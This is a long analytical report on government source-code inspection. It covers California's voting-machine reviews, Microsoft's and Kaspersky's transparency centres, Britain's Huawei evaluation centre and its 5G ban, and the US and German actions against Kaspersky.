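Some of the makers had received warnings before 2007. In February 2006, Wagner and colleagues reviewed version 1.96.6 of Diebold's scanner software and version 4.6.4 of its touchscreen software. They recommended rewriting some of the code but judged that counties could manage the risk in the meantime. Government Technology reported at the time that Bruce McPherson, Bowen's predecessor, approved the machines on condition that Diebold make all the recommended long-term changes and submit the new version for federal testing. Hoke and Kettyle's list of Diebold software certified in California in 2007 has the same two version numbers, so more than a year later the promised rewrite had not replaced the old code there.

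Sequoia's record was similar. Consultants for Alameda County reported weaknesses in its voting system in October 2006, and Blaze and colleagues found some of the same weaknesses in the code they received eight months later.

After Bowen's decision, Sequoia told reporters that it would make the necessary improvements, and Hart promised to comply with her requirements, according to Yahoo! News. Most of the conditions concerned how counties installed, guarded and checked the software, so complying did not necessarily require changing it. The California Secretary of State was still revising the conditions for the same numbered version of Diebold's software in December 2009, and did not withdraw approval from all the company's systems until August 2019.

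These records show only what California allowed, and a vendor could have improved a later product or one it sold in another state. There was also little reason to expect quick repairs, because Blaze and others believed that the makers needed to redesign the systems completely. Every modification required new approval, so a vendor with a conditionally approved product would have found it easier to keep selling it than to correct it. In 2019, security researchers who ran a voting machine workshop at the DEF CON hacking conference still found vulnerabilities in voting hardware in use in the United States (DEF CON Voting Village, *DEF CON 27 Voting Village Report*, 2019).

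### The lost ballots in Humboldt County

In the November 2008 election, a fault in Diebold's software, not an attack, left 197 ballots out of the certified results in Humboldt County, in northern California. Volunteers working with the county discovered the omission by scanning every paper ballot again and counting the images with separate software. Bowen's office reported in March 2009 that the county's central software, GEMS 1.18.19, could silently drop the first batch of scanned ballots when an operator deleted a different batch. The company had known about the fault since 2004.

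The top-to-bottom review did not cover that version. Bishop's red team and Hoke and Kettyle both worked on GEMS 1.18.24. The Humboldt case therefore shows that counties could still be using software the review had not examined, but it does not prove that the reviewers overlooked the fault.

The reviewers might have missed the fault even if they had examined the right version, because they were looking for ways to tamper with an election, not for mistakes in deleting batches. The volunteers found it without reading any code, by comparing the machine's total with the ballots. Their method would have worked on any version, whether the cause was an accident or an attack, but only after the election.

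### How California examines voting systems now

California now relies less on federal approval. It adopted its own voting system standards, and in February 2019 the California Secretary of State (2019) announced a plan to withdraw approval from systems that had not been tested against them. The Diebold products lost their approval this way. The state required replacements for the old systems without ever establishing that the vendors had repaired them.

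A company that wants to sell a new voting system now applies to the state before any county can use it. The California Secretary of State asks who owns and controls the company, and requests technical documents and a log of changes to the product. Testing takes months and includes source code review, red team attacks and accessibility checks, according to the California Secretary of State's *Election Cybersecurity*. Bowen ordered this kind of testing as a special investigation, but it is now a normal part of approval. The state can also approve a system conditionally and withdraw that approval later, under Public.Law's *Elections Code section 19201*.

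California has also partly addressed a question that the 2007 reviewers left aside: whether the software in use is the software the state examined. *Primary Election* (Rodriguez, 2026), a memorandum from the Secretary of State's office to county officials, explains that counties may install only a "trusted build" supplied by the state. Before every election, each county must either reinstall that build or compare hashes to confirm that nobody has altered its copy. The state therefore does not have to rely on the vendor to install the right version, whereas Britain had to rely on Huawei.

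A matching hash cannot reveal a fault that was already in the approved software, such as the one in Humboldt. California still relies on paper ballots to catch such faults. Every registered voter receives one, and after every election each county must count a sample by hand and resolve any differences from the machine's result.

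## What can governments see at Microsoft's and Kaspersky's transparency centres?

Governments that join Microsoft's programme can read the source code of Windows, Office and a few other products, but apparently cannot build it and compare the result with the software Microsoft sells. Kaspersky offers to let visitors build its code and make that comparison, and also shows them the updates and detection rules it sends to customers. No government appears to have published what it found under either programme, although an agency may have described a visit in one of its own reports.

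### Why Microsoft opened its code

When Microsoft announced its Government Security Program in January 2003, it was losing government customers to Linux, whose source code anyone can read and change. In June 2002, the German government had signed a contract with IBM to help its agencies adopt Linux (Galli, 2003, *Microsoft Launches Government Security Program*). NATO and the Russian body Atlas joined Microsoft's program at its launch. Atlas's head, Boris Girichev, said in Microsoft's announcement that the lack of source code had made Russian authorities less willing to use the company's products.

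Secrecy was only part of the problem, though. ESJ's *Microsoft Opens Up Its Source Code* (2003) described an internal Microsoft memo, leaked two months before the launch, about what attracted customers to open-source software. They rated two arguments highest, that it was cheaper and that it avoided royalties to American companies. Letting governments read Windows source code could not change either. But Helm thought, in *Office Source for Governments* (2004), that read-only access diluted one of the main advantages of open-source products.

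Microsoft decided which governments could join the programme. It had identified more than 60 eligible countries, about a third of the world's total, based on their laws on and attitudes to intellectual property (Bekker, *Microsoft Opens Source Code to Some Governments*). Membership was free, and each government could choose whether to disclose it. By September 2004 the programme had about 30 members, including China and the United Kingdom (Bekker, 2004, *Government Source Code Review Program Expanded to Office*).

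The transparency centres came a decade later, after Edward Snowden, a former contractor for the US National Security Agency, leaked documents in 2013 showing that the agency captured large amounts of email data handled by American technology companies. Microsoft opened a centre at its Redmond headquarters in 2014, another in Brussels in 2015, and two more in Singapore and Brasília in October 2016. Microsoft (2016) also mentioned plans for a fifth in Beijing. The company now advertises four centres, without naming them. Membership grew from 23 governments and international organisations in 2015, according to Microsoft, to more than 40 today, represented by over 100 agencies.

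### What Microsoft shows

An agency's staff can use a secure website called Code Center Premium to browse and search the source code of Windows, Office, SharePoint, Exchange and SQL Server, but they cannot change it. Microsoft suggests using the site to learn how a feature works, review coding practices or look for vulnerabilities. Agencies typically have to study the code there before they visit a transparency centre, where they can analyse it in more depth.

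The centres hold far too much code for visitors to read. The Brasília centre displayed as many as 50 million lines for Microsoft's email and server products, according to Fortune's *How Microsoft Is Trying to Calm Fears About Spy 'Back Doors'* (2016). One person would need about 250 years to read them once at 100 lines an hour, the rate the California reviewers assumed. Visitors therefore need tools that scan code for suspicious patterns.

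Microsoft's Scott Charney said that governments could review products "both manually and by running tools" (Vanian, 2016, *Here’s One Way Microsoft Is Trying To Improve Relations in China*). *Microsoft opens up source code, offers cyber security expertise to governments* (Siew, 2016) reported that they could use their own tools at the Singapore centre. But when the Brasília centre opened, Fortune reported that it was unclear whether visitors could run the deep analysis needed to find backdoors.

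Visitors also probably cannot build the code. In 2003, ESJ reported that members could view it in a debugger, a tool for following a program step by step as it runs, but could not compile or modify it. Directions on Microsoft's *Government Access to Source Code Expanded* (2003) stated that they could modify some security features, so the early terms are not entirely clear. Microsoft's current descriptions do not mention building the code or comparing it with the shipped product. Unless the private agreements allow more, visitors have to trust Microsoft that the code they inspect matches the software on their computers. HCSEC had much the same problem with Huawei for years.

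Microsoft offers less access to its cloud services, which run in its own data centres. Members can get confidential documents about them and talk to engineers, but Microsoft's *Technical Data* states that this part of the programme excludes source code.

Documents may not tell governments enough. In *Federal Cyber Experts Thought Microsoft’s Cloud Was “a Pile of Shit”*, Dudley and Burke (2026) investigated FedRAMP, the American programme that approves cloud services for federal agencies. In 2024 its evaluators complained of a "lack of proper detailed security documentation" for one of Microsoft's biggest cloud products, but FedRAMP approved it anyway. FedRAMP is separate from the Government Security Program, whose members may have received better documents.

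### A visit to a Microsoft centre

A national agency applies through its local Microsoft representative and signs an agreement. Its staff then read the code online so they can arrive at the centre with specific questions. Galli noted in 2003 that Microsoft did not disclose the licence restrictions.

At the Brasília centre, visitors had to leave all electronics outside the viewing room. The computers inside had no internet connection and displayed copies of the code from local servers. If visitors wanted to use their own tools, Microsoft presumably had to load them first. Visitors could question developers face to face. Nobody could copy the code, and the copies Microsoft kept for the visit were later deleted.

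Visitors therefore leave without any code. Microsoft does not explain in its public descriptions of the programme whether they may keep notes or scan results, or publish a flaw they find. A government may disclose that it belongs to the programme, but the licence could still forbid it to describe the code.

### What Kaspersky shows

Kaspersky announced its Global Transparency Initiative in October 2017, after the US Department of Homeland Security banned federal agencies from using its products. The company promised a review of its source code by "an internationally recognized authority" (Meyer, 2017, *Kaspersky Really Wants People and Governments to Trust It Again*). The outside assessments it has publicised since then have mostly examined its procedures rather than the code.

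Kaspersky opened its first centre in Zurich and added another in Madrid in 2019. In its latest sustainability report, Kaspersky (2026) counts 13 centres across Europe, Asia, Latin America, the Middle East and Africa. It has closed its centre in the United States.

Not all of Kaspersky's centres offer source code. The Rome and Utrecht centres opened with only an overview of how the company develops software and handles data. Kaspersky calls this option the "blue piste", after the easy ski runs, and said at the time that visitors requested it more than any other. It has three levels of review, and the most demanding covers the critical parts of the source code in detail. Security MEA's *Kaspersky expands its network of Transparency Centers* describes the options as read-only and suited to visitors' skills and interests.

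A visitor could not learn everything an antivirus program can do from its source code alone. The program checks files against a database of detection rules, which describe what malicious files look like. If the user has agreed, Kaspersky's products send suspicious files to the company for analysis. If someone added a rule that matched a phrase common in secret government documents, the program might flag those documents and send them to Kaspersky, even though its source code had not changed.

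Kaspersky therefore lets visitors examine its detection rules, all versions of its updates, and the source code of the cloud services that receive and store customers' data. This is broader access than Microsoft describes, but visitors can check only the rules that exist on the day of their visit.

Visitors can compile a product and compare it with the public version, which deals with HCSEC's matching problem, at least for one version of one product. But Kaspersky's experts help run the process, and the company supplies the build scripts. A careful visitor would bring a copy of the product bought from an ordinary shop, and would still have to consider whether the compiler was trustworthy.

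### Swiss data centres and outside audits

Kaspersky also moved some of its data processing to Switzerland, which it describes as a neutral region. In November 2018 two data centres in Zurich began to handle the suspicious files that European users had agreed to share. By November 2020 they also served users in the United States, Canada and much of Asia, and they later added users in Latin America and the Middle East.

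But the company still has a data centre in Moscow. Its certificate under ISO 27001, an international standard for managing information security, lists Moscow along with Zurich, Frankfurt and Toronto. A server's location also does not show who can log in to it.

Kaspersky also had a more ambitious plan, scheduled for after 2018, to move the assembly of its software, including products, updates and detection rules, and to appoint an independent third party to manage and review the work. The milestones in its summary of the initiative include the completed data move but nothing about software assembly. If the company still builds its products in Russia, the Swiss data centres do little to address the fear that someone in Russia could alter an update.

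Kaspersky relies mainly on audits to answer that fear. Since 2019, accountants have used a standard called SOC 2 to examine how it develops and releases its detection rules. The first audits checked its safeguards at one point in time, and a 2023 audit covered six months. *«Лаборатория Касперского» прошла независимый аудит SOC 2* (2026), from the Russian technology site CNews, reported that the company had passed again in September. The auditors concluded that controls protected the rules from unauthorised changes, which is useful evidence that the rules are safe from a rogue employee or an intruder. It is much weaker evidence that the company's own managers haven't approved a harmful rule, perhaps under pressure from the state, because that change would be authorised.

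### A visit to a Kaspersky centre

A government agency applies to Kaspersky by email and must be legally responsible for cyber security in its country. Businesses that use Kaspersky's products, or are thinking of buying them, can also apply. Kaspersky was still considering whether to admit academics, journalists and independent security researchers, the people most likely to publish what they found.

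The visitor chooses a level of review and can ask for development documents, a list of the software's components, source code, rules or a build. Kaspersky's staff explain the material and answer questions. They will stop anyone who tries to modify the code and will report abuse to the local police. The company's descriptions differ on how much of this can be done remotely. One description includes remote source code review, while Kaspersky's page about the centres limits remote access to the overview.

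Kaspersky provides the material "for consultation purposes only". Like Microsoft, it does not say publicly whether visitors can take notes away or publish their conclusions. Customers can request the full SOC 2 report, so they may find it easier to get an accountant's opinion of the company's procedures than another government's opinion of its code.

### Few reviews and no public findings

The centres do not seem busy. Kaspersky counted 67 visits and seven completed product reviews between the start of the initiative and its report for 2024–2025, which is fewer than ten visits a year across all its centres. It had spent more than $9.4 million on the whole initiative. The company does not say how many of the visitors came from governments.

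An earlier Kaspersky report gave a much higher figure of 60 product reviews by the end of 2023. A cumulative total cannot fall from 60 to seven, so the company may have been counting overviews as reviews. The same report listed 34 visits for 2022 and 2023 and set a target of at least five for 2024.

Microsoft does not appear to publish comparable figures. It said in 2015 that the Redmond centre had hosted "several governments" in almost a year.

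Governments' public statements amount to expressions of goodwill. When New Zealand joined Microsoft's programme, a participant quoted by Microsoft (2003) said the agreement gave agencies "reassurance" that they had the information to build secure systems. An unnamed Brazilian official told Reuters that the Brasília centre was "a good step". Kaspersky displays testimonials from government bodies in Vietnam, India, Indonesia and Thailand, but these bodies had taken part in its training programme, which is different from reviewing its products.

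Visitors may have published no serious flaws because they found none, reported them privately or agreed not to publish. Many may have seen only an overview. The public cannot tell which explanation is right, so the lack of published flaws is not evidence that the code is good.

### Can customers verify for themselves?

Mark Estberg, who ran Microsoft's government security programme, promised too much when he said in Brasília that governments could "verify for themselves that there are no back doors". The California reviewers doubted they would have found a disguised backdoor in a system less than a fiftieth the size of the code on display in Brasília.

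The vendors' better argument is that some access is preferable to none. Most governments could not force Microsoft or Kaspersky to hand over source code, and a reading room lets them investigate a specific concern, such as how a product encrypts data. It may also deter a vendor from planting a backdoor, because any visitor might find it. Most competitors also offer less. A study that Kaspersky promotes found that only three of 14 security vendors had transparency centres, according to IT Voice.

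But deterrence depends on how likely a thorough inspection is, and seven product reviews in about seven years is not many for a company with a wide range of products.

Anastasiya Kazakova, who worked in public affairs at Kaspersky, made a more theoretical case in *Global Transparency Initiative as a framework for increasing trust in cyberspace*. She compares the company's measures to the confidence-building measures that rival states adopted during the Cold War to reduce the danger of accidental conflict, and warns that banning vendors out of mistrust fragments the internet and hampers innovation. But the measures in one of her examples, an agreement that 35 states reached in Stockholm in 1986, were politically binding and verifiable, whereas Kaspersky wrote the rules of its centres itself and can change them unilaterally.

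The open-source news site FOSS Force argued that Microsoft opened its centres to stop foreign governments from considering alternatives such as Linux. Microsoft clearly has a commercial interest, but that does not make the code it shows less genuine. The more serious objection is that the vendor decides who can inspect the code, for how long and on what terms, and has no duty to fix the problems inspectors find.

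Code that governments are free to read can still contain many serious flaws. In April 2026 alone, the AI model Mythos found 90 "critical" and 141 "important" bugs in Microsoft's SharePoint, according to an internal slide described in a ProPublica article that Techdirt republished. SecurityWeek's *Microsoft Opens Transparency Center in Europe* recorded that SharePoint was already among the products open to members in 2015. Some of the bugs may have been in newer code, and governments may have reported others over the years. Still, after more than a decade of government access, a better tool found hundreds of serious flaws. Visitors' ability to bring such a tool into a transparency centre may now matter more than how long they can stay.

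Kaspersky's bug bounty, which pays outsiders who report flaws, has produced clearer results than its centres. By the end of 2023 the company had paid $81,750 for 59 reports. One group of researchers earned $23,000 for reporting a flaw that could have let an attacker run programs on a user's computer with system privileges, which Kaspersky then fixed. The company has not published a comparable example from a visit to a centre.

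### Compared with Banbury and California

One advantage of the reading rooms over HCSEC is that the inspectors work for the government that sends them, not the vendor. But Kaspersky's ban on agencies with offensive capabilities would probably exclude Britain's NCSC, since it is part of GCHQ, which also carries out offensive operations. The ban therefore keeps out some of the people best able to find a well-hidden backdoor.

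Visitors can choose what to read from the available material, as the California reviewers chose which code to study. They have less time than HCSEC's permanent staff did, since members' early visits to Redmond lasted one or two weeks. They also see nothing like the operators' networks that HCSEC recreated, although a government can later test a suspicion on its own copy of Windows.

Because access is voluntary, the vendor can narrow it on its own. Microsoft reasonably did so in July 2025 with a separate scheme that gives security companies early warning of vulnerabilities. Bloomberg Law's *Microsoft Curbs Early Warnings to China Firms About Flaws* (2025) reports that Microsoft restricted the warnings for firms in countries that require them to report vulnerabilities to the government, such as China, after investigating whether a leak had led to attacks on SharePoint.

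Because the findings are not public, the vendors are also under less pressure to fix problems. Neither vendor advertises anything like California's combination of public reports and private appendices. Microsoft said in 2003 that it would work closely with members to address their concerns, which left it free to decide what to change.

A dissatisfied government can still stop buying, as China has largely done. China had joined Microsoft's programme by 2004, and Microsoft later made a special edition of Windows 10 for it. Yet Microsoft has said that no foreign operating system, including Windows, has been considered compliant with the procurement guidelines China introduced in 2017. CTech's *Microsoft once saw China as unthinkable to leave* reports that Reuters examined six Chinese government buying guides published between December 2023 and May 2026, and that five recommended no Microsoft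 products. China also wanted to promote its own software industry, so it might have stopped buying Windows regardless of what its inspectors had read.

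## Why were Huawei and Kaspersky excluded after opening their code?

Britain excluded Huawei from its 5G networks after American sanctions threatened to force a redesign of the products HCSEC had spent years learning to inspect. The United States and Germany acted against Kaspersky because the Russian government might make the company misuse its software, a risk that did not depend on what the source code contained at the time. None of the three governments said inspectors had found a backdoor.

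### January 2020: Huawei stays, within limits

On 28 January 2020 the British government finished a review of telecoms suppliers and decided to keep Huawei out of the most sensitive parts of the networks but allow it elsewhere. That day the NCSC published advice on what it called high risk vendors (NCSC, 2020). Operators could use such a vendor's equipment only if the NCSC had designed and was overseeing a plan to manage the risk. Huawei was the only vendor with a plan, and the NCSC described HCSEC as a fundamental part of it, so inspection had become a condition of selling in Britain.

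Ministers made this decision knowing what HCSEC had found. Lord Scriven, a Liberal Democrat, read the Oversight Board's "limited assurance" verdict to the House of Lords the same day (Parallel Parliament's *Tuesday 28th January 2020*, 2020). The government told Parliament that it remained confident in the arrangements but that HCSEC "alone cannot mitigate all the risks" (Parallel Parliament's *Huawei*). The limits on where operators could put the equipment were meant to address some of the remaining risks.

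Some of that remaining risk was unrelated to code. In 2013 the Intelligence and Security Committee said that most concerns about Huawei related to its perceived links to the Chinese state. In 2020 the government said that it had considered such links when it classed the company as high risk.

### What the American chip rule changed

The May 2019 sanctions had done Huawei less harm than they might have, because in most cases they covered only equipment with more than 25% American content, and Huawei had stockpiled parts in advance. It also replaced many American chips with ones designed by its subsidiary, HiSilicon. The NCSC thought HCSEC could manage the extra work of examining the modified products.

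On 15 May 2020 the United States moved to restrict the supply of the replacement chips. Hogan Lovells' *U.S. Department of Commerce announces expansion of foreign direct product rule* (2020) explained that the new rule extended American export controls to certain foreign-made goods destined for Huawei. A factory anywhere in the world now needed an American licence to make a Huawei-designed chip with American tools, even if those tools played only a small part in the work. Chipmakers used such tools so widely that the NCSC did not think any supplier could make Huawei's designs without breaking the rule. It expected shortages within three to twelve months, depending on how many chips Huawei had stored.

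The NCSC considered four ways in which Huawei might go on supplying Britain:

- **Ignore the rule.** Huawei said it would not do this, and the government would not have accepted it. The United States might have responded with a stricter order that stopped Huawei from supporting equipment already in the networks.
- **Buy general-purpose chips from other companies.** Huawei would have had to rebuild some products around parts they were not designed for. Its record in software engineering gave the NCSC no confidence that it could do so safely, and the United States could easily have extended the rule to these chips too.
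- **Make chips without American technology.** Huawei or its partners would have needed new design software and new factory equipment as well as new chips. The NCSC called this "a truly Herculean task" that would normally take decades.
- **Wait for the United States to relent.** The NCSC thought this unlikely.

### Why redesigned products would be harder to inspect

Most of what HCSEC's staff knew was about particular products. By 2020 they knew where the weak components were, which repairs Huawei had promised and how each operator used the equipment. Rebuilding a product around different chips would have made some of that knowledge obsolete.

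The NCSC expected Huawei to develop new manufacturing tools under extreme time pressure, which would probably increase the number of defects and make them harder to repair. HCSEC would also have had to examine the tools, since a faulty or corrupt tool can introduce flaws into a product whose design is sound, as Ken Thompson had pointed out about compilers. HCSEC could not recruit quickly enough for the extra work, so it would have examined fewer products. The NCSC concluded that gaining confidence in the new equipment would be extremely difficult and might be impossible.

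The rule also appeared to prevent Huawei from sending affected equipment, or even designs and binaries, to HCSEC. Moving the centre to a separate company that November dealt with this problem but could not make unfamiliar products easier to assess.

### July 2020: the government orders removal

On 14 July Oliver Dowden, the culture secretary, told Parliament that operators must stop buying Huawei's 5G equipment at the end of the year and remove their existing Huawei 5G equipment by 2027. He estimated that the restrictions would delay 5G by two to three years in total and cost up to £2 billion, according to Computer Weekly's *Huawei technology banned from UK national comms infrastructure*.

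The government treated home broadband differently. Only two major suppliers, Nokia and Huawei, made access equipment for fibre networks, and the NCSC thought depending on one would be more dangerous than keeping both for a short transitional period. It admitted that it could not guarantee to manage the risks of Huawei's redesigned fibre products. The level of assurance the NCSC required therefore depended partly on what else operators could buy.

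The NCSC's published analysis supports the ban on new 5G equipment better than it supports the order to remove installed equipment. The NCSC's revised plan continued to cover Huawei's existing 5G products, which the American rule had not altered. The NCSC also rejected removing Huawei from all fixed and mobile networks, because replacing so much equipment quickly would have been riskier than keeping it. The government's removal order was narrower, covering only 5G and allowing seven years, but the analysis contains no argument for it.

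Politics may explain the difference. Meyer (2020), in *The U.K. is finally banning Huawei’s 5G equipment*, wrote that the government had given in to pressure from the United States and many Conservative members of parliament. Huawei complained that "this is about US trade policy and not security" (TechHQ's *Huawei to be stripped from UK 5G networks by 2027*). But a trade rule can create a real security problem, and the NCSC explained in some detail how this one did. The NCSC also expected the United States to keep tightening the sanctions until they worked, so even a purely technical assessment had to consider American policy.

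### The legal directions of 2022

At first, operators had only the government's announcement and the NCSC's advice. The Telecommunications (Security) Act 2021 gave ministers the power to restrict particular vendors, and in October 2022 they used it to send 35 operators legally binding directions. The UK government's *Huawei legal notices issued* (2022) lists the main deadlines.

| Deadline | What operators had to do |
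|---|---|
| Immediately | Stop installing new Huawei equipment in 5G networks |
| 28 January 2023 | Remove Huawei from sites significant to national security |
| 31 October 2023 | Limit Huawei to 35% of the full fibre access network |
| 31 December 2023 | Remove Huawei from the core, the central part of the network |
| End of 2027 | Remove Huawei from 5G networks |

Ministers had delayed the deadlines for fibre and the core by several months because a few operators warned that rushing could cut customers off. The directions also barred operators from installing sanction-affected Huawei equipment in full fibre networks. This ended the exception the NCSC had made in 2020, when it planned to concentrate HCSEC on those products.

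The government again said that the NCSC could no longer manage the security of Huawei's products because of the sanctions. But it also sent Huawei a separate notice listing all its reasons for considering the company a national security risk, and the sanctions were only one of them.

### How far removal has got

The public cannot easily tell how much Huawei equipment remains. The minister Chris Bryant said in October 2024 that the directions contained twelve requirements, and that the only remaining deadlines were at the end of 2025 and the end of 2027 (Parallel Parliament's *Huawei* (2024)). In January 2026, *Huawei swap-out blamed as London 5G lags UK rivals* (Tarre, 2026) reported that replacing the equipment had taken longer than expected. It quoted a connectivity specialist who blamed the replacement work for London's 5G falling behind that of other British cities.

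In March 2026, someone asked the telecoms regulator, Ofcom, whether the four big mobile companies had met each deadline. Ofcom replied that it did not hold a list of breaches (*Freedom of Information request*, 2026). It collects information on operators' progress and reports to the technology secretary, who decides whether they have complied. Ofcom also warned that it might refuse future requests on national security grounds. In April 2026, a minister told Parliament that operators who disobeyed the directions faced financial penalties, but gave no figures for removal (Parallel Parliament, *Telecommunications*, 2026).

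### What became of HCSEC

The Oversight Board does not appear to have published another report after June 2021. City AM's *Dorries blamed as Huawei watchdog report goes unpublished for two years* repeated a Telegraph claim that Nadine Dorries, then culture secretary, had decided to shelve publication. Work in Banbury was continuing at the time, but it was unclear whether anyone was still writing annual reports. Former Conservative leader Iain Duncan Smith asked why the government was not releasing them.

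The government has since closed the HCSEC Oversight Board. The Department for Science, Innovation and Technology said that the committee's examination of Huawei's equipment had ended and that "stronger departmental governance arrangements" had replaced it, according to TelcoTitans' *UK government shutters Huawei oversight committee despite continued presence*. Without published findings, outsiders cannot tell whether these arrangements are stronger. In 2021 the Board had reported the NCSC's view that HCSEC would remain essential for as long as operators used Huawei's equipment.

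HCSEC's holding company still exists. CorpSignals' *Cyber Security Evaluations Limited* shows that it filed accounts for 2024 and, in December 2025, a routine annual statement. These filings do not establish whether its staff still evaluate products. If they do, they should have little new equipment to examine, because operators are restricted in what they may install, but Huawei's older products still need software updates.

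Company registry data published by Endole lists directors who sit on the boards of both the holding company and Huawei's main British subsidiary. That is unsurprising for two companies in one group, and HCSEC's managing director used to have separate authority to run the centre. But the public relied on the Oversight Board to report each year whether that separation worked.

### Did inspection fail?

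After ten years of inspection, Britain had "limited assurance" about Huawei's products, had seen no general improvement in the company's engineering, and faced the cost of removing its equipment. The inspection centre, HCSEC, may have increased that cost by making operators comfortable enough to keep buying. The arrangement failed if its aim was to let the country rely on Huawei indefinitely.

The timing, however, does not suggest that poor findings caused the exclusion. When the government decided in January 2020 to keep Huawei, it had already received two "limited assurance" verdicts. The NCSC still thought it could manage the risk, and it changed its advice six months later because of the American rule. Better findings might have made the NCSC more optimistic about redesigned products, but HCSEC would still have lacked the staff to examine them.

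The government defended inspection by claiming to know more about Huawei and its risks than any other country did (Parallel Parliament). That knowledge mattered in July 2020, when the NCSC had to judge how well Huawei would cope with a difficult redesign. It could draw on years of evidence about the company's engineers instead of relying on Huawei's promises. Inspection therefore informed the decision, although ministers could have reached the same one for political reasons without it.

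### The American directive against Kaspersky

Kaspersky was first excluded before it opened its code. In September 2017 the US Department of Homeland Security gave federal agencies 30 days to identify Kaspersky products on their systems, 60 days to plan their removal and 90 days to begin it. Eugene Kaspersky, the company's founder, had offered that July to let American officials examine the source code, but the company did not announce its transparency initiative until October.

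A code review would have done little to address the department's concerns. Antivirus software can read almost every file on a computer and has high privileges, which an attacker could exploit. The department was also worried about ties between some Kaspersky officials and Russian intelligence, and about Russian laws that let the intelligence agencies compel companies to help them. It argued that the Russian government could exploit the software with or without Kaspersky's co-operation.

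Congress passed a law that December banning federal use of Kaspersky's products. Kaspersky challenged both measures in court and lost. In 2018 an appeals court held that Congress had acted to protect government systems, not to punish the company.

### Germany's warning

Germany's Federal Office for Information Security (BSI) warned against Kaspersky's antivirus software on 15 March 2022, three weeks after Russia's full-scale invasion of Ukraine. It advised users to switch to other products but did not ban the software. The BSI explained that antivirus software needs extensive privileges and a permanent encrypted connection to its maker's servers, and that customers cannot inspect this connection. It said a Russian company might attack its customers willingly, be forced to attack them, or fall victim to an operation it knew nothing about.

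Kaspersky replied that the warning was political and did not rest on a technical assessment of its products. The second claim was largely right. Between January and March, the BSI had changed its view of the danger from Russia, while Kaspersky's code had presumably stayed much the same. That does not make the warning unreasonable, because the danger from a trusted product depends partly on who might give orders to its maker.

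When Kaspersky tried to have the warning withdrawn, an administrative court in Cologne found the company's safeguards, including its Swiss data centres, insufficient against interference by the state. The court thought constantly monitoring the source code and updates would be practically impossible, because the code was complex and the updates were frequent. A higher court also ruled against Kaspersky that April.

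### The American prohibition of 2024

In June 2024 the US Department of Commerce went further and banned Kaspersky from supplying antivirus and cyber security software to anyone in the United States. The company had to stop new sales on 20 July and updates on 29 September. The department was concerned that Russia could use Kaspersky to collect Americans' data, install malicious software or withhold updates. It also worried about products from other companies that contained Kaspersky's code, since their buyers might not know it was there.

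Kaspersky had proposed letting a trusted third party verify the security of its products, but the Commerce Department decided that only a complete prohibition would deal with the risk. The department considered whether Russia could use the products to harm the United States, not how well they detected malware. Kaspersky answered that the department had relied on the geopolitical climate and theoretical concerns instead of thoroughly evaluating the integrity of its products.

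Kaspersky had a fair complaint about the evidence, since the department did not publish an example of a malicious update. But a government that waits for a malicious update may discover it only after the damage is done. The two sides disagreed mainly over whether the ability to cause harm justifies a ban without proof that anyone has used it, and a cleaner inspection report would not have resolved that.

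Kaspersky's departure from the American market showed how much control it had over its customers' computers. In September 2024, its software removed itself from many American users' computers and installed UltraAV, another company's antivirus program. Kaspersky had arranged the switch to keep its customers protected after the ban and had emailed them about it, but some said they had not expected a new program to install itself.

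### Which worries could an inspection settle?

The British government worried about Huawei's links to the Chinese state from the beginning, but for years it thought inspection and careful network design could keep the risk tolerable. The American and German authorities did not think inspection could keep the risk from Kaspersky tolerable. These judgments differed partly because the companies sold different kinds of products.

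| Worry | What inspectors can establish | What remains uncertain |
|---|---|---|
| Flaws in the current version | Many of the flaws, given time and the right build | Flaws that nobody found |
| A harmful update | Whether an update is safe, if they see it before customers install it | Later updates, and urgent ones that cannot wait |
| Privileged access | What the product can read, change and send | Whether anyone will misuse that access |
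| Loss of support | How much customers depend on the vendor | Whether the vendor will go on supplying repairs |
| A government's power over the vendor | Almost nothing | Whether the government will use it |

The Cologne court's objection is much stronger for antivirus software than for base stations, partly because antivirus updates are more urgent. A telecoms operator can often delay an update while someone tests it, and checking updates was HCSEC's main job at first. An antivirus company may send out new detection rules many times a day, and customers who wait for an inspector to check them have no protection against the newest threats.

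An independent body could check each update and distribute it, much as California supplies counties with a trusted build of their voting software. The vendor could no longer send anything directly to customers. This would make secret changes harder, but the body would need enough skilled staff to keep up with the updates, and it might still miss a well-disguised backdoor.

Privileged access poses a different problem, because a product can cause harm while working exactly as its designers intended. By Kaspersky's own account, in 2014 its software flagged an archive on an American user's computer as malicious and sent it to the company for analysis. An analyst found that it contained source code for hacking tools that researchers have linked to the US National Security Agency. Kaspersky said it deleted the archive and gave it to nobody. Any harm depended on what people at the company did with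 the file after receiving it. A reviewer could have read every line of the antivirus program without finding a fault, because collecting suspicious files is one of its normal functions.

Inspecting a product cannot remove a government's legal power over the company that makes it. Moving staff, ownership and control of updates to another country might reduce that power, but these are changes to the company, so someone would have to verify them with corporate records and access logs. Even then, the government could pressure employees who still had family or property within its reach.

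This argument applies to many companies besides Huawei and Kaspersky. American law can also compel American companies to help their government, and Microsoft's products have extensive privileges and receive frequent updates. A government that excludes only some foreign vendors is therefore also deciding which foreign governments to trust.

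## When may a government demand source code, and what are the dangers?

A government can usually demand source code as a condition of sale unless a trade agreement forbids it, and those agreements have exceptions. The main danger is that officials who inspect a product to protect their own country also learn how to attack everyone else who uses it. Russian inspectors, for example, were reading the source code of American security products while American officials worried about what Russia could do through Kaspersky's software.

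### Russia's reviews of Western software

In June 2017 a Reuters investigation, carried in Fortune's *More Tech Giants Are Bowing to Russian Demands for Security Secrets* (2017), found that Cisco, IBM, SAP, Hewlett Packard Enterprise and McAfee had let Russia review source code. Russia asked for the code of firewalls, antivirus programs and software containing encryption before it would allow their sale. FSTEC, a Russian defence agency, reviewed the code of 13 Western products between 1996 and 2013, and carried out 28 reviews in the three years before the article. Microsoft had opened Windows code to Russia much earlier, but under a programme that many governments joined.

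Many of the requests came from the FSB, the Russian security service, which also approves sales of advanced technology. A company that refused a review could wait indefinitely for approval to sell in a market worth an estimated $18.4 billion that year. The American government says the FSB took part in the 2014 theft of data from 500 million Yahoo accounts, which the FSB denies.

The companies tried to limit what the inspectors could take away. Reviews often took place in "clean rooms", where nobody could copy or alter the code. McAfee held them on its own premises in the United States and SAP held them in Germany. Cisco said it sometimes showed regulators small parts of its code, after searching those parts for vulnerabilities. That search was probably the most useful precaution, because an inspector in a clean room can still remember a flaw, and a flaw can be as short as the attempted Linux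 backdoor, which was two lines long.

None of the American officials who spoke to Reuters could name a hack that a review had made possible. This is only weak reassurance, because an attack rarely shows how the attacker learned of the flaw. Attackers also find many flaws without source code, though, so the added danger from the Russian reviews is plausible but unproven.

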